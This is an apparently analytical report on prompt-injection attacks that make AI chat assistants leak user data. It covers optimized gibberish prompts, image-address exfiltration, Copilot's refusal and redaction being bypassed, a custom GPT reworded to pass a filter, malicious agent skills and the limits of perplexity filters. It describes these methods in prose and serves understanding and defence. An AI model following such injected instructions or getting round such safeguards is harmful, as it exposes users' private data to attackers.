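Mistral wrote that "no user was impacted and no data was exfiltrated," but didn't explain how it knew. In an image leak, the user's browser sends the stolen data straight to the attacker's server, so Mistral's own servers would have no record of the request. The company could have searched stored replies for image addresses at unfamiliar domains, and may have done so. Its statement is easy to believe for the optimized prompts, because the researchers didn't publish them until five weeks after the fix. It's less certain that nobody used a plain-English version in the six and a half months between LeChat's launch and the fix.

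Mistral didn't publish its reasons for the medium rating. The attacker had to trick each victim into pasting a prompt and got only some of their personal details, which supports that rating. But the attack was also very reliable and hard for the victim to notice, which suggests a higher one. Mistral did accept that there was a flaw, which Schwartzman had not been able to get OpenAI to do a few months earlier.

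### ChatGLM's month of silence

The researchers tried several channels before ChatGLM's team answered. A footnote in the paper gives one of them, issue 592 in the public GLM-4 repository, where the developers publish the open-weight model and take bug reports. The leak was in the chat product, though, and the people who answer questions about the open-weight model may not be able to change the product's web page.

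What happened next is unclear. A copy of THUDM's *Issues* (2024), the repository's list of open reports, from mid-November 2024 or later shows older and newer issues but not number 592, so someone had probably closed it by then. This is weak evidence of a fix, because developers also close issues that they have passed on to colleagues or that don't concern the repository's code. The company behind the GLM models has since changed its name from Zhipu AI to Z.ai, according to an assessment of a later GLM model by CAISI (2026), a US government body that evaluates AI models.

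The researchers published while ChatGLM was still vulnerable. They posted complete, ready-to-copy prompts on their project page and told readers that they should be able to reproduce the attack on ChatGLM. They had first reported the flaw to ChatGLM's team 31 days earlier. GitHub had taken 15 weeks to fix the same kind of flaw, and OpenAI had taken eight months.

Some points support the researchers' decision to publish. ChatGLM's team had said nothing for 30 of those 31 days, and people who use a product have an interest in knowing that it leaks. The published prompts sent the stolen data to the researchers' own domain, so an attacker would have had to substitute another domain and check that the prompt still worked, or run a new search with the researchers' public code. Neither would have been hard for someone with a suitable graphics card and a day to spare. But the image leak itself had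 been public knowledge since the spring of 2023, so keeping quiet about the optimized version would have protected ChatGLM's users from only part of the danger.

### After the fix

If Alice, the job applicant, pastes the same prompt into LeChat on September 14, the model still follows it and writes her details into an image address. But the page now shows a placeholder instead of fetching the image, so her browser never contacts the attacker's server.

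The placeholder makes the attack slightly easier to notice than the blank reply did, but Alice probably wouldn't realize from it that someone had tried to steal her personal data.

According to the paper, Mistral disabled external images, but the project page describes it as disabling all markdown images. The paper's narrower description fits better with what came later, since LeChat gained an image generator in November and had to display the pictures it made. Pictures that Mistral makes and stores itself don't require the browser to contact an outside server.

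Mistral could have tried to defend against the prompt instead. The simplest way would have been to reject any message containing the researchers' prompt, but an attacker could then have computed a new one within a few days. Retraining the model to resist such prompts would have taken longer than four days and protected only that model. Fu and colleagues reported results for LeChat only with Mistral Nemo, one of several models Mistral had released by then. A change to the page works whichever model writes the reply.

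The fix does not protect other products. Mistral Nemo is an open-weight model, so anyone can build a chat page around it, and a page that loads external images would be vulnerable to the same prompts. Protection can also differ between one company's apps. Anthropic had dealt with the leak on Claude's web page in July 2023, but in December 2024 Willison (2024) quoted Rehberger's announcement that Anthropic had just fixed a leak through image addresses in Claude's iPhone app. Rehberger added that mobile apps often have this problem.

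Data can also leak in other ways when images are blocked. The model can write an ordinary link with the stolen details in its address, under inviting text such as "Download your improved letter". Fu and colleagues didn't try this attack. It is less reliable because nothing is sent until the user clicks, and a careful user can inspect the address first.

The researchers also tried tools that open web addresses without a click. Their prompts for ChatGLM's browsing tool worked well on the open-weight model but weren't tested on the product. Copying Mistral's fix would not have changed ChatGLM's browsing tool.

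A browsing tool is also more dangerous than an image in one respect. The model reads whatever the tool returns, so an attacker's server could answer the first request with a page of further instructions. An image displayed to the user doesn't normally go back to the model.

### Was it worth losing the images?

Willison approved of Mistral's fix and thought all chat interfaces should lock down markdown images in the same way. Fu and colleagues accepted that restricting an assistant's tools protects against their attack, but argued that it makes the assistant less useful and so may be a poor choice in the longer term.

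The researchers cited Meta's assistant as an example of a restricted one. It could only consult Wolfram Alpha, a service that answers mathematical and factual questions, and search a fixed set of websites. These restrictions had kept it off the researchers' list of targets, and they also prevented it from opening a page the user chose or showing a picture from that page.

These positions differ less than they seem to, because Willison was writing about images and the researchers about tools in general. In his note on Embrace The Red's report about GitHub Copilot Chat, Willison also did not object to a fix that, as he understood it, still allowed images from trusted domains. A product can therefore follow his advice and still show charts from sites that its maker controls.

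They differ, however, over how much usefulness to give up while nobody can make the model itself reliable. An image leak succeeds only if the model writes the image code correctly, with probability p, and the page loads the image, with probability q, so the chance of a leak is p × q.

Better training reduces p, the chance that the prompt works. As an invented example, suppose 5,000 people paste a malicious prompt that works every time, and the company then retrains its model so that the prompt works only 2% of the time. If the page still loads every image, 5,000 × 0.02 × 1 = 100 people lose their data. If the company publishes the new model's weights, attackers can run another search on them and raise p again. Mistral's fix instead set q, the chance that the page loads the image, to zero for external images. No prompt can raise q as long as the block has no gaps, so the company doesn't have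 to predict new attacks.

Blocking external images probably made little difference to LeChat's users in September 2024. Without web search, the model could offer only image addresses that it remembered from training or found in the user's text, and probably few people relied on those. Web search makes external images more useful, because an assistant that has read an article about a building could show a photograph of it. A company that has blocked all external images then has a reason to allow some again, and each exception could let data leak.

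Willison had the better argument about images. Displaying them is a convenience, the leak had already appeared in several products, and a company can keep much of the benefit by serving images from its own domain.

The researchers' worry carries more weight for agents that are meant to open web pages, send emails or make bookings. Fu and colleagues warned that the same kind of prompt could make an assistant book unwanted hotels, delete a user's data or leak files. Mistral's approach would prevent those attacks only by removing the functions that people use the agents for.

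But the researchers doubted that the other defense they discussed, filtering out prompts with high perplexity, would be reliable. That left companies to decide for each tool which actions an assistant could take without asking the user. Mistral had decided not to let its assistant load external images automatically.

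## Since 2024: do people run prompts written by strangers?

Fu and colleagues predicted at the end of their paper that people would share malicious prompts and use them by mistake, just as they do with malware. By 2026 this had happened with instructions that people install as add-ons for AI agents, and companies were hiding promotional prompts in web links. There is much less evidence for the case in the paper, where someone copies a prompt from a website and pastes it into a chat.

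### Would anyone paste gibberish?

An unreadable prompt may look too suspicious for people to run. Someone who wants help with a cover letter has no reason to expect it from a mixture of Cyrillic, Tamil and stray punctuation, and an empty reply gives them another reason to be suspicious. An attacker might do better with a long, readable prompt that does improve cover letters but has one harmful line in the middle.

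A study of readable prompts supports this doubt. In *LLM Whisperer*, Lin, Gerchanovsky and colleagues (2024) replaced a few words in shopping prompts with synonyms chosen to make a model mention a particular brand. They showed each of 845 people an original or altered prompt with a model's answer, and asked how clear the text was, whether they would use it and whether anything stood out. In 42 of 48 comparisons, the ratings for the two versions were statistically equivalent. The altered version did clearly worse in only one of the other six. Among people shopping for a TV, 80% of those shown the altered version listed the target brand among the recommendations, compared with 34% of those shown the original.

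Lin and colleagues assumed that people who notice nonsense in a prompt may stop using it, but they didn't test gibberish. Their attack is also easier to hide than an image leak. A few synonyms can make a model favor a brand without looking odd, but a leaking prompt normally has to include the attacker's web address and tell the model to put private details in it.

BGR's *Chatbot Hack Shows Why You Shouldn't Trust AI With Your Personal Data* suggests that an attacker would put the gibberish inside a larger, useful prompt. That might make the gibberish harder to notice, but the Imprompter prompts were made to produce only the image code. To get a useful answer as well, the attacker would probably have to run a new search with target replies that contain both, as the researchers did for their altered pictures in 2023.

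Willison, however, thought a user might more easily fall for a prompt whose purpose was unclear. Gibberish may make people uneasy, but they can't tell from it that their data is at risk.

An unreadable prompt could put off many people and still be useful to an attacker. On LeChat, the optimized prompt T10 leaked about twice as many personal details per conversation as the plain-English prompt, so it would collect more data in total if people pasted it more than about half as often. The tests don't show how often people would paste one compared with the other, and they didn't cover a harmful line inside a long, useful prompt.

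### The comparison with ClickFix scams

People do run text they don't understand. Programmers copy commands from forums, and other users copy settings from help pages, often to fix something that is broken.

Criminals exploit this habit in scams that security companies call ClickFix. A web page shows a fake error message or a fake test to prove that the visitor is human. The instructions on the page are to paste a command into a window on the computer and press Enter, supposedly to solve the problem, but the command installs malware. The page has often already put the command on the clipboard, much as Samoilenko's page added an instruction to copied text, so the victim may never look at it.

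These scams show that unreadable text doesn't put everyone off. But people expect a computer command to look cryptic and a prompt to look like a request. A ClickFix page also presents its command as the only way past an obstacle, whereas a gibberish prompt on a sharing site competes with readable ones. An attacker can gain more from a command, which can take over a computer, than from a prompt in a simple chat, which can steal only what the assistant can access. The comparison makes the cover-letter scenario more plausible, but we can't use it to estimate how many people would fall for such a prompt.

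An attacker who plants the prompt in a web page or email for the assistant to read doesn't have to persuade anyone to run it. But gibberish is less useful there for hiding the prompt's purpose from people, because the attacker can write it in plain English and make the text invisible.

### Prompt libraries and custom GPTs

Fu and colleagues wrote that an attacker could post a malicious prompt on PromptBase, a marketplace for prompts, or on ShareGPT, where people publish their chatbot conversations. Lin and colleagues cited the web-hosting company GoDaddy's library of advertising prompts as an example of a site where people use prompts written by others. Both groups described possible attacks, and neither reported a real one on these sites.

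Custom GPTs, versions of ChatGPT that users can build and share, are a simpler way to get people to run a stranger's instructions. The builder writes the instructions in advance, and other users normally don't see them, so the instructions don't need to look convincing or be unreadable.

In November 2023, Rehberger built a custom GPT called "Thief" as a demonstration. Embrace The Red's *Malicious ChatGPT Agents* reports that Thief offered to play tic-tac-toe but first asked for personal information, which it sent to his server through a hidden image. Thief asked for an email address to personalize the game and for a password as part of a "security process", according to SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server*.

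OpenAI's automatic check blocked the first version of the GPT, which contained words such as "steal" and "malicious". Rehberger changed the wording, and it passed. He then limited the GPT to people with the link so it wouldn't appear in OpenAI's public store. He reported it on November 13, and OpenAI closed the report two days later as "Not Applicable".

Some real GPTs have also broken OpenAI's rules. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) reports that Shen and colleagues examined 755,297 GPTs and found 2,051 violations, or about one for every 370 GPTs. The violations included harmful content as well as privacy leaks, so the figure doesn't show how many GPTs were built to steal data.

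### Links that fill in the prompt

Many assistants accept a prompt in a link to their own site. The link can contain the prompt after "?q=", and the page puts it in the input box when it opens. Some assistants run it immediately, so a victim who clicks the link submits a stranger's prompt without copying anything, and perhaps without reading it.

*Reprompt* (2026), a report by the data security company Varonis, demonstrated a data theft from the personal version of Microsoft's Copilot that needed only one click. Copilot usually refused to open a web address without a good reason, and it could remove sensitive data from the address before opening it. The researchers got around the refusal by presenting the task as a puzzle about a picture of a bird. The data removal covered only the first request, so they told Copilot to do everything twice and compare the results. In one test, Copilot removed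 a secret phrase from the address on the first attempt but sent it on the second.

The attacker's server then answered each request with another instruction, first for the user's local time, then for their location, then for everything Copilot had learned about them, and finally for a summary of their last conversation. The theft continued even if the user closed the Copilot tab. The prompt in the original link was readable, but someone who read it couldn't have known what the attacker would ask for. An attacker can therefore hide the purpose of a theft without using gibberish, by keeping most of the instructions on a server.

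Microsoft had fixed the flaw by the time Varonis published its report in January 2026. PointGuard AI's *Copilot "Reprompt" Attack Enables Session Hijack and Data Exfiltration* says there was no evidence that anyone had used it in a real attack. In June, Varonis reported a similar attack on Copilot's enterprise search. It also started with a pre-filled link, and it could reach any company data the user had access to.

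Companies were already using pre-filled links on real people, but to promote themselves. Microsoft (2026) reviewed links to AI assistants in email traffic over 60 days and found 50 different prompts from 31 companies, one of which sold security products. Most of the links were behind "Summarize with AI" buttons. A visitor who clicked one got a summary of the page, but the prompt also told the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source. Free tools let website owners add such buttons.

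Microsoft says that every case it found came from a legitimate business. It doesn't report how many people clicked or how often the assistants followed the instructions, and it notes that the effect varied between assistants. The report shows that ordinary companies will hide instructions from users when it's easy and might bring in customers. The cases Microsoft observed all used links, but it also lists pasted prompts as a possible way to plant such instructions and advises against pasting prompts from untrusted sources.

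### Instruction files for agents

The clearest real abuse involves skills, which people download to teach an agent a new task. A skill is a folder of written instructions, usually in a file called SKILL.md, that sometimes includes small programs. The agent reads the instructions and can run the programs with the user's permissions. Anthropic introduced skills in its coding agent Claude Code in October 2025, and within three months two public registries listed more than 98,000.

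Liu and colleagues checked all 98,380 skills in those registries. Pattern-matching software and a language model first picked out 4,287 suspicious ones. The researchers ran these on isolated systems with fake passwords and keys, and watched for attempts to steal these credentials or contact undocumented servers. Two researchers then reviewed the 762 that triggered an alarm and confirmed 157 as malicious. One was called "email" and secretly copied every message to the attacker. Another was presented as a calculator but gave the attacker control of the computer.

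One actor was responsible for 54.1% of the malicious skills, which imitated well-known brands. The registries removed all 157 after the researchers reported them. The true number of malicious skills was probably higher, because each test session lasted at most 60 seconds and some skills were programmed to wait for a particular trigger.

The researchers found 632 flaws in these skills, 84.2% of them in the SKILL.md files. Flaws in those files aren't necessarily prompt injections, since a written instruction can simply tell the agent to download and run a harmful program. About a third of all the flaws involved manipulating the agent itself, for example by telling it to ignore its safety rules or hide something from the user.

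Other audits looked at skills for OpenClaw, a popular open-source agent with a marketplace called ClawHub. *Hundreds of Malicious Skills Found in OpenClaw's ClawHub* (Underhill, 2026) describes an audit by Koi Security, and *ClawdPwned* presents another. Snyk (2026), a software security company, scanned ClawHub and another marketplace.

| Audit | Skills checked | What the auditors counted | Result |
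|---|---|---|---|
| Liu and colleagues | 98,380 | Malicious behavior confirmed by tests and review | 157 (0.16%) |
| Koi Security | 2,857 | Malicious skills | 341 (11.9%) |
| *ClawdPwned* | 2,556 | Likely malicious skills | 49 (1.9%) |
| Snyk | 3,984 | Skills with a critical security flaw | about 13% |

The shares differ so much partly because one campaign, ClawHavoc, accounted for 335 of Koi's 341 malicious skills. Without it, Koi's figure would be 6 out of 2,522, or 0.24%, close to Liu and colleagues' result. Snyk instead counted skills with serious flaws, which an author can introduce without meaning any harm. *Beyond Maliciousness* (2026) criticizes earlier research for not measuring malicious intent and dangerous capabilities separately in the same set of skills.

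Lakera, another security company, linked 44 malicious skills to ClawHavoc and counted more than 12,559 downloads of them. Some of those downloads may have come from researchers or automated programs, and a download doesn't prove that an agent ran the skill. Even so, many people seem willing to install instructions from strangers when the instructions are packaged as a useful add-on.

The most common trick resembles a ClickFix scam, in which the victim wants to get something done and treats the harmful step as part of the setup. *MalSkillBench* (2026) examined 703 malicious skills from ClawHub and found that 607 (86.3%) offered a harmless-looking task but required the user or agent to install something else first. This fake requirement delivered the malware. The high share reflects a few large campaigns, though, so it is better evidence of what those attackers preferred than of which trick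 works best.

Many attackers made little effort to disguise their malicious agent skills. *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026) scanned live marketplaces, and many of the skills its software flagged used words such as "malicious" or "stealer" openly. Reviewers confirmed just under 200 malicious skills, and only 82 of them hid their purpose behind functions that looked legitimate.

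Fu and colleagues were therefore right that people would share and install malicious instructions, but skills give an attacker more access than the LeChat prompts in their study, which could steal details only from a single conversation. A skill can read files and passwords on the user's computer.

### Have attackers used optimized prompts?

It is unclear whether anyone has used an optimized data-leaking prompt against real users. The promotional prompts Microsoft found were in plain language. Liu and colleagues' list of 13 attack techniques includes encoded programs and instructions in invisible characters, but has no category for unreadable prompts produced by optimization.

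This is only weak evidence that attackers don't use such prompts. Microsoft published search queries to help companies find the promotional links, but the queries search for words such as "remember" and "trusted", which a data-stealing prompt doesn't need. Liu and colleagues tested only the skills that their first scan had flagged. If that scan missed a skill with a gibberish instruction, the skill would never have reached the tests that could have caught it leaking data. Image leaks are also hard to discover afterward.

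Attackers may also have had little reason to use optimized prompts. T10 took 60 hours to compute and was made for one company's model, while an attacker can write a plain-English instruction in minutes and try it on many agents. The extra work is worthwhile only if a person or a filter would have stopped the plain-English version, and the two registries that Liu and colleagues studied didn't vet the skills they listed.

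## Since 2024: why unreadable prompts work and whether filters stop them

Xiaohan Fu, the lead author of the Imprompter paper, has suggested that language models learn relations between tokens that go beyond natural language. If so, T10, the main prompt for stealing personal data, is a proper instruction that people can't read. A simpler explanation is that a few familiar words in the prompt produce the behavior and the rest have no effect. The difference matters for defense because a filter needs a feature that reliably separates these prompts from ordinary text. Experiments since 2023 mostly support the simpler explanation, but the unfamiliar tokens also seem to have some effect.

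### Does the model ignore the odd tokens?

Melamed, McCabe and colleagues (2023), in *Prompts have evil twins*, took 100 ordinary prompts, such as "Describe the star formation process", and collected 100 replies to each from Vicuna 7B, an open-weight chat model. They then used GCG, the search algorithm behind Imprompter, to find garbled prompts that made the same replies likely. For n replies, they measured how far a garbled prompt was from the original like this:

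difference = (1/n) × [log P(reply₁ | original) − log P(reply₁ | garbled) + … + log P(replyₙ | original) − log P(replyₙ | garbled)]

A difference of zero means that, on average, the garbled prompt makes the replies as likely as the original does. The garbled version of the star prompt scored 4.4, so it made a typical reply about 80 times less likely than the original did, which is a small gap for a reply of many tokens. GPT-4's reconstruction of the prompt from the same replies, "What leads to the creation of new stars?", is good English but scored 16.3, so it made a typical reply about 12 million times less likely.

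The garbled prompts also worked on other companies' models. GPT-4, acting as judge, gave the top rating to 75 of 100 replies from Gemini Pro, 62 from GPT-4 itself, 54 from Claude 3 Sonnet and 36 from Claude 3 Haiku.

If the model needed only a few keywords, replacing the other tokens should make little difference. The researchers replaced each of the first six tokens in turn with a marker meaning "unknown". This generally changed the replies more for garbled prompts than for ordinary ones, which supports Fu's idea that the strange tokens matter. But the prompts they tried on other models had started from GPT-4's English guesses and often kept words from them, such as "of stars" in the garbled star prompt. Those readable words may account for much of the prompts' effect.

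In *Evil twins are not that evil*, Rakotonirina, Kervadec and colleagues (2024) examined the odd tokens more closely. They computed 208 ten-token prompts that each made Pythia 6.9B, an open-weight model that simply continues text, write a particular phrase. They could shorten 73% of these prompts without changing the output. They then tried replacing each remaining token with each of the 10,000 most common tokens. About three-quarters of the remaining tokens had at least one substitute that left the output unchanged.

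Some tokens were fillers that the researchers could replace with hundreds of unrelated ones. They could replace others only with closely related tokens, such as "Irish" in place of "Ireland". The last token was almost impossible to replace, and the output usually followed it as naturally as one word follows another in normal text.

These results help explain the earlier experiment. A filler token can look essential if the "unknown" marker is the only substitute tested, even though many other tokens could replace it. Some of the tests had similar effects on ordinary English, and Rakotonirina and colleagues concluded that unreadable prompts arise from the way models process language in general. They got similar results on five other Pythia and OLMo models, only one of which had been trained to follow instructions. In a chat product, formatting tokens come between the user's prompt and the reply,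 so the last token of a prompt like T10 may matter less.

### Reading scrambled text

Duan, Zhao and colleagues (2025), in *Unnatural Languages Are Not Bugs but Features for LLMs*, tested how much meaning models can recover from gibberish. They shuffled the words of short texts, added exclamation marks and ran a search similar to GCG until two small models, Mistral 7B and Vicuna 7B, could translate the result back into English. They then gave the gibberish to other models and asked questions about it in normal English.

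One set of texts described things that don't exist, so the models couldn't answer from memory. The other set consisted of 100 easy math problems. For comparison, the researchers also used the original texts and the shuffled ones from which the search had started. The table shows the percentage of correct answers:

| Model | Facts: original | Facts: shuffled | Facts: optimized | Math: original | Math: shuffled | Math: optimized |
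|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3 8B | 99 | 29 | 63 | 58 | 18 | 50 |
| Gemma 2 9B | 98 | 35 | 65 | 97 | 21 | 41 |
| Llama 3 70B | 97 | 73 | 93 | 100 | 38 | 75 |
| GPT-3.5 | 98 | 73 | 93 | 91 | 32 | 53 |
| GPT-4o | 98 | 61 | 88 | 95 | 25 | 53 |

Further tests on Llama 3 8B suggested that the model relies mostly on words from the original text and uses the question that follows to help infer how they fit together. Results were much worse when the search excluded the original words, which favors the keyword explanation. But the shuffled texts also contained all the original words, and every model in the table did better with the optimized versions, on both facts and math. The search must have added useful information, either through the new tokens or by putting the original ones in a better order.

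It is less clear how models get meaning from fragments. *À la recherche du sens perdu* (2025) proposes that the way software splits text into tokens plays a part, and that models learn to remove filler characters, such as exclamation marks placed after each letter of a word. The paper calls this pure speculation.

### Why some words stay readable

The attackers in the Imprompter scenario want a prompt that works but looks meaningless. In *Prompt Obfuscation for Large Language Models*, Pape, Mavali and colleagues (2024) wanted the same thing for defense. Companies often keep their system prompts secret, but users can trick an assistant into repeating them, so the researchers tried to replace a system prompt with gibberish that would be useless to a thief.

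They used GCG to find ten tokens that would make Llama 3.1 8B answer as if it had received an instruction such as "Reply with a pirate accent." The hidden versions worked well. Answers with the hidden prompts scored 33 on BLEU, a measure of shared wording, compared with 37 for a second set of answers with the original prompts and 18 for answers without them.

However, the hidden pirate prompt included the words "Speak pirate tone", and the one for "Answer like a robot" included "robotic behavior". The search had started from random tokens, so these words couldn't be left over from an English draft. When Pape and colleagues penalized readable text in the search, the prompts became harder to read, but the answers matched the originals less well on all eight measures.

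The researchers did hide the instruction completely. A model converts each token into a list of numbers before processing it, and they optimized those numbers directly instead of choosing tokens. The optimized numbers worked at least as well as the original prompts and didn't correspond to any text. So a model can follow an instruction that doesn't exist in any human language, as Fu's hypothesis would suggest. But nobody can paste these numbers into LeChat, because a chat box accepts only text.

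The Imprompter prompts show the same tension between function and disguise. Fu and colleagues concede in a footnote that T10 seems to reveal something about its purpose, but they argue that readers can see this only once they know what the prompt does. They have a point. Rakotonirina and colleagues could pick out the important tokens in their prompts fairly reliably, but they had the model's output in front of them, whereas a user like Alice, the job applicant, has only the prompt.

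Some of what looks like noise to an English speaker in T10 is also text in other languages, which a multilingual model can read. One fragment is the Hindi word for "name", in a prompt that asks for names. Fu's hypothesis therefore seems partly right. Models respond to combinations of tokens that no person would write, but the combinations that work usually contain recognizable pieces of the task, sometimes in several languages.

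### Filtering by perplexity

The simplest filter for gibberish uses perplexity, a measure of how unlikely a text is according to a language model. The company chooses a threshold, scores each incoming prompt with its own model, and either blocks prompts above the threshold or asks the user to confirm them.

These prompts look easy to filter, judging by Fu and colleagues' figures. On Llama 3.1 70B, ordinary prose scores below 10, their handwritten English instructions scored at most 616, and the 12 finished prompts scored between 1,905 and 56,927. A threshold of 1,000 would therefore block all 12 and let through all the handwritten instructions.

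The calculation changes if Alice pastes the prompt together with her letter. Suppose the letter has 400 tokens and a perplexity of 8, and T10 has 50 tokens and keeps its perplexity of 7,489 when it follows the letter. The filter averages the logarithms over the whole message:

perplexity = exp( (400 × log 8 + 50 × log 7,489) / 450 ) ≈ 17

The message passes the filter easily. Even T8, the prompt with the highest perplexity, would raise the score only to about 21. To catch such prompts, the filter has to score short stretches of text separately, so that the 50 strange tokens aren't averaged with the whole message.

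Checking short stretches produces more false alarms, because people often paste harmless text that is hard to predict. One example is a random 16-character code of upper- and lowercase letters and digits, such as a software license key. If the model reads it two characters at a time, each token has 62 × 62 = 3,844 equally likely possibilities, so the code's perplexity is about 3,844, twice that of T9, the least surprising of the 12 prompts. One such code in a paragraph wouldn't matter much, but a pasted list of them would score higher than a real attack.

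Even a filter with a low false alarm rate can raise far more false alarms than real ones. Suppose a product gets 100 million messages a day, of which 100 contain a malicious prompt. A filter that catches every attack and wrongly flags 0.1% of the other messages would raise about 100,000 false alarms a day. Only about one alarm in a thousand would be real, and users would soon learn to click through the warnings.

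The more serious objection is that an attacker can write a prompt with low perplexity. The search for T9 began from rough English text that had a perplexity of only 128 and made Mistral Nemo write a correct image in 77% of tests. A filter with a threshold of 1,000 would have blocked T9 but let the English text through.

An attacker can also make the search prefer more natural text. Melamed and colleagues tried this on Vicuna in 2023 by adding a penalty for improbable prompts. The resulting prompts contained fewer strange tokens, but they matched the original better than the version without the penalty in only 30% of cases. They still beat GPT-4's English guesses 81% of the time. The task was to imitate ordinary prompts, which allows more error than writing image code that must be exact, so the penalty could reduce a prompt's effectiveness more in an image leak.

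A perplexity filter thus forces attackers to use readable prompts but doesn't stop the attack. This helps somewhat when a person has to paste the prompt, because a readable instruction to put private details in a web address may put them off. It helps little when the assistant fetches a web page by itself, since an attacker can hide plain-English instructions in the page.

### Trained detectors

A trained detector learns from examples of attacks, so it can look for malicious wording as well as gibberish. In *Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents*, Alizadeh, Samei and colleagues (2025) tested one on a simulated banking agent that used GPT-4o. The detector, made by ProtectAI, read everything the agent's tools returned and stopped the agent if it found an injection.

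A false alarm would therefore interrupt a legitimate task. The researchers tested four defenses, and the detector was the only one that didn't make the agent worse at its tasks both with and without an attack. Some of the defenses stopped every leak on the 16 tasks of an existing benchmark, but none did when the researchers extended the test to 48 tasks. This suggests that success on a small benchmark is weak evidence of how well a detector will work in new situations.

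All of the attacks in that test were readable. To catch gibberish ones, a company could instead examine the numbers a model computes while reading a prompt. In *Demystifying optimized prompts in language models*, Melamed, McCabe and Huang (2025) recorded these numbers for optimized and ordinary prompts in 17 open-weight models from the Gemma 2, Llama 3.2, Qwen2.5, SmolLM2 and Pythia families, each with at most 3 billion weights. The researchers also trained a small model of their own on children's stories.

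A simple classifier using only a few of these numbers distinguished the two kinds of prompt with high accuracy. The same method did little better than chance at separating ordinary prompts from random ones, so it may have detected something more specific than strangeness. In the chat-trained models, an optimized prompt and its ordinary counterpart looked similar in the early layers, diverged in the middle and converged again near the end. This partly fits Fu's hypothesis, since the model seems to reach the same reply by a different route. But switching off the most distinctive numbers disrupted ordinary prompts about as much as optimized ones, so the experiment didn't reveal a separate mechanism for optimized prompts.

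The researchers proposed using such a classifier to warn a provider before the model has finished processing a suspicious prompt. This would add little computation, because the model computes the numbers anyway. But they tested it on matched pairs of prompts, half of them optimized, so the results don't show how many false alarms it would raise among millions of real messages. They also didn't test it against an attacker who searches for prompts that also fool the classifier.

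### Better searches

Attackers have also gained new ways to search for these prompts. Labunets and colleagues' 2025 attack on Gemini showed that attackers don't always need a published model similar to the target. In 2026, a project called Claudini used AI agents to discover new search algorithms. If agents can keep improving the search, the 60 hours that T10 took are a poor guide to how long it will take to find such a prompt in future.

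Other attackers could avoid gibberish altogether. In *ContextLeak*, Jia, Wang and colleagues (2026) optimized the readable name and description of a tool that people might install for their AI agent. The attacker needs only an ordinary copy of the agent and no model weights. The method works roughly like this:

1. A language model writes several candidate names and descriptions for the tool.
2. The attacker adds each candidate to the context of an invented user, with a realistic task, chat history and list of other tools.
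3. The agent decides whether to use the tool and what information to send to it.
4. A candidate scores highly if the agent chooses the tool and sends it a close copy of the invented user's private context.
5. The attacker trains the language model on these scores and repeats the process.

The training pushes the language model to write descriptions that make private information sound necessary for the tool to work. These descriptions contain no strange text for a perplexity filter to find and no open command to leak anything. Jia and colleagues used the method to steal users' prompts, chat histories and tool lists, and it still worked when the victim's agent ran on a different model from the one used in training. They found existing text detectors insufficient against it. Training models to resist injections wasn't a good solution either, because it often made them worse at choosing harmless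 tools.

Nobody seems to have published a retest of the Imprompter prompts on the models that replaced Mistral Nemo and GLM-4-9B. The nearest evidence is the 2026 test in which GCG injections computed on a small Qwen model hardly ever worked on GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5. But Imprompter relied on a model closely related to its target, so that result doesn't rule out that a new prompt computed on a company's latest open-weight model would work on the company's assistant.

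### Is optimization still needed?

Several studies have extracted private data from newer models with readable text. In their banking test, Alizadeh and colleagues injected a message written as if it came from the user, which included the model's name and a request to email private details to a stranger. It worked about 20% of the time on most of the six models tested (GPT-4o, GPT-4 Turbo, GPT-3.5 Turbo, Claude 3.5 Sonnet, Llama 3 70B and Llama 4 17B) and 40% of the time on Llama 4, the most vulnerable.

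Compliance varied widely between requests. When the message asked for the account balance and address, Claude 3.5 Sonnet complied in 93% of tests. When it asked only for the password, every model except Llama 4 refused every time. Samoilenko had noticed in 2023 that ChatGPT readily leaked earlier messages but not passwords, and the banking test suggests that safety training makes models more likely to refuse requests containing the word "password". Models were more likely to leak the password when the message also asked for other details.

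Wording can greatly affect how often an attack works. Yang, Na and Choi (2026), in *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection*, planted instructions in a web page and asked ChatGPT 5.3 to summarize it. An older trick that makes the assistant's task look already finished worked in 4 of 136 attempts. A new one that presents the user's request and the start of the page as only an example worked in 121 of 168, or 72%. Both were in Korean, and neither required gradient-based optimization. The attacker had to guess roughly what the user would ask, which isn't hard for a page that people want summarized.

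The 72% is how often ChatGPT followed the planted instruction, not how often it leaked data. Yang and colleagues demonstrated a leak separately, on ChatGPT 5.2. The assistant opened the malicious page, then a second page with material meant to overcome its safety training, and finally an address containing an invented user's birthday. The three requests reached the researchers' server within five seconds. This shows the attack was possible in February 2026, but one demonstration can't establish a success rate. The second page also drew on a jailbreak method that manipulates tokens, so the full attack may not have depended on plain language alone.

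The broadest test of readable requests covered 363 models. Serpa, Rocha and Pedrini (2026), in *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets*, put a random code in each model's system prompt with an instruction never to reveal it. An AI agent, steered by a researcher, then tried to persuade each model to reveal the code, and 296 did so at least once. More than half of the successful attempts involved switching to another language, most often French.

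The attacker talked to the model directly and could keep trying, so this wasn't a theft from an innocent user. The code was meaningless, so the result doesn't show how readily the models would reveal personal data. But it does show that an attacker can often get around an explicit instruction to keep something secret without computing a prompt from the model's weights. A prompt in French or Korean also hides its purpose from anyone who can't read the language, and writing one takes no computing time.

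Yang and colleagues' results suggest that careful wording can now provide much of the reliability that T10 got from optimization in 2024, although nobody has compared the best readable prompt with an optimized one on the same current product. Optimized gibberish is probably still useful mainly as a disguise in the cover-letter scenario, where a person sees the prompt before the model does. A perplexity filter also has the best chance of stopping it there.

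## Since 2024: how image blocking has held up

Mistral ended the Imprompter leak in 2024 by stopping LeChat's page from loading external images. Many other companies let their assistants load images from some external addresses, and in 2025 and 2026 researchers repeatedly sent data out through those allowed addresses. Where a product blocked images altogether, researchers often found another feature that could contact a server.

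### Approved sites that strangers could use

In 2025, Rehberger got ChatGPT to send him a user's chat history, although OpenAI was still using url_safe, the check on image addresses it had introduced in 2023. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* explains that url_safe approved addresses under windows.net, where anyone can rent online storage from Microsoft and read the log of requests to it. After Rehberger rented storage there, a malicious web page or PDF could make ChatGPT write private text into the address of an "image" in his storage, and the text appeared in his log.

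Google's Bard had a similar weakness in 2023, but Rehberger's new attack could steal more because ChatGPT had started putting details of the user's recent conversations into its system prompt. One malicious document could therefore expose earlier chats as well as the current one.

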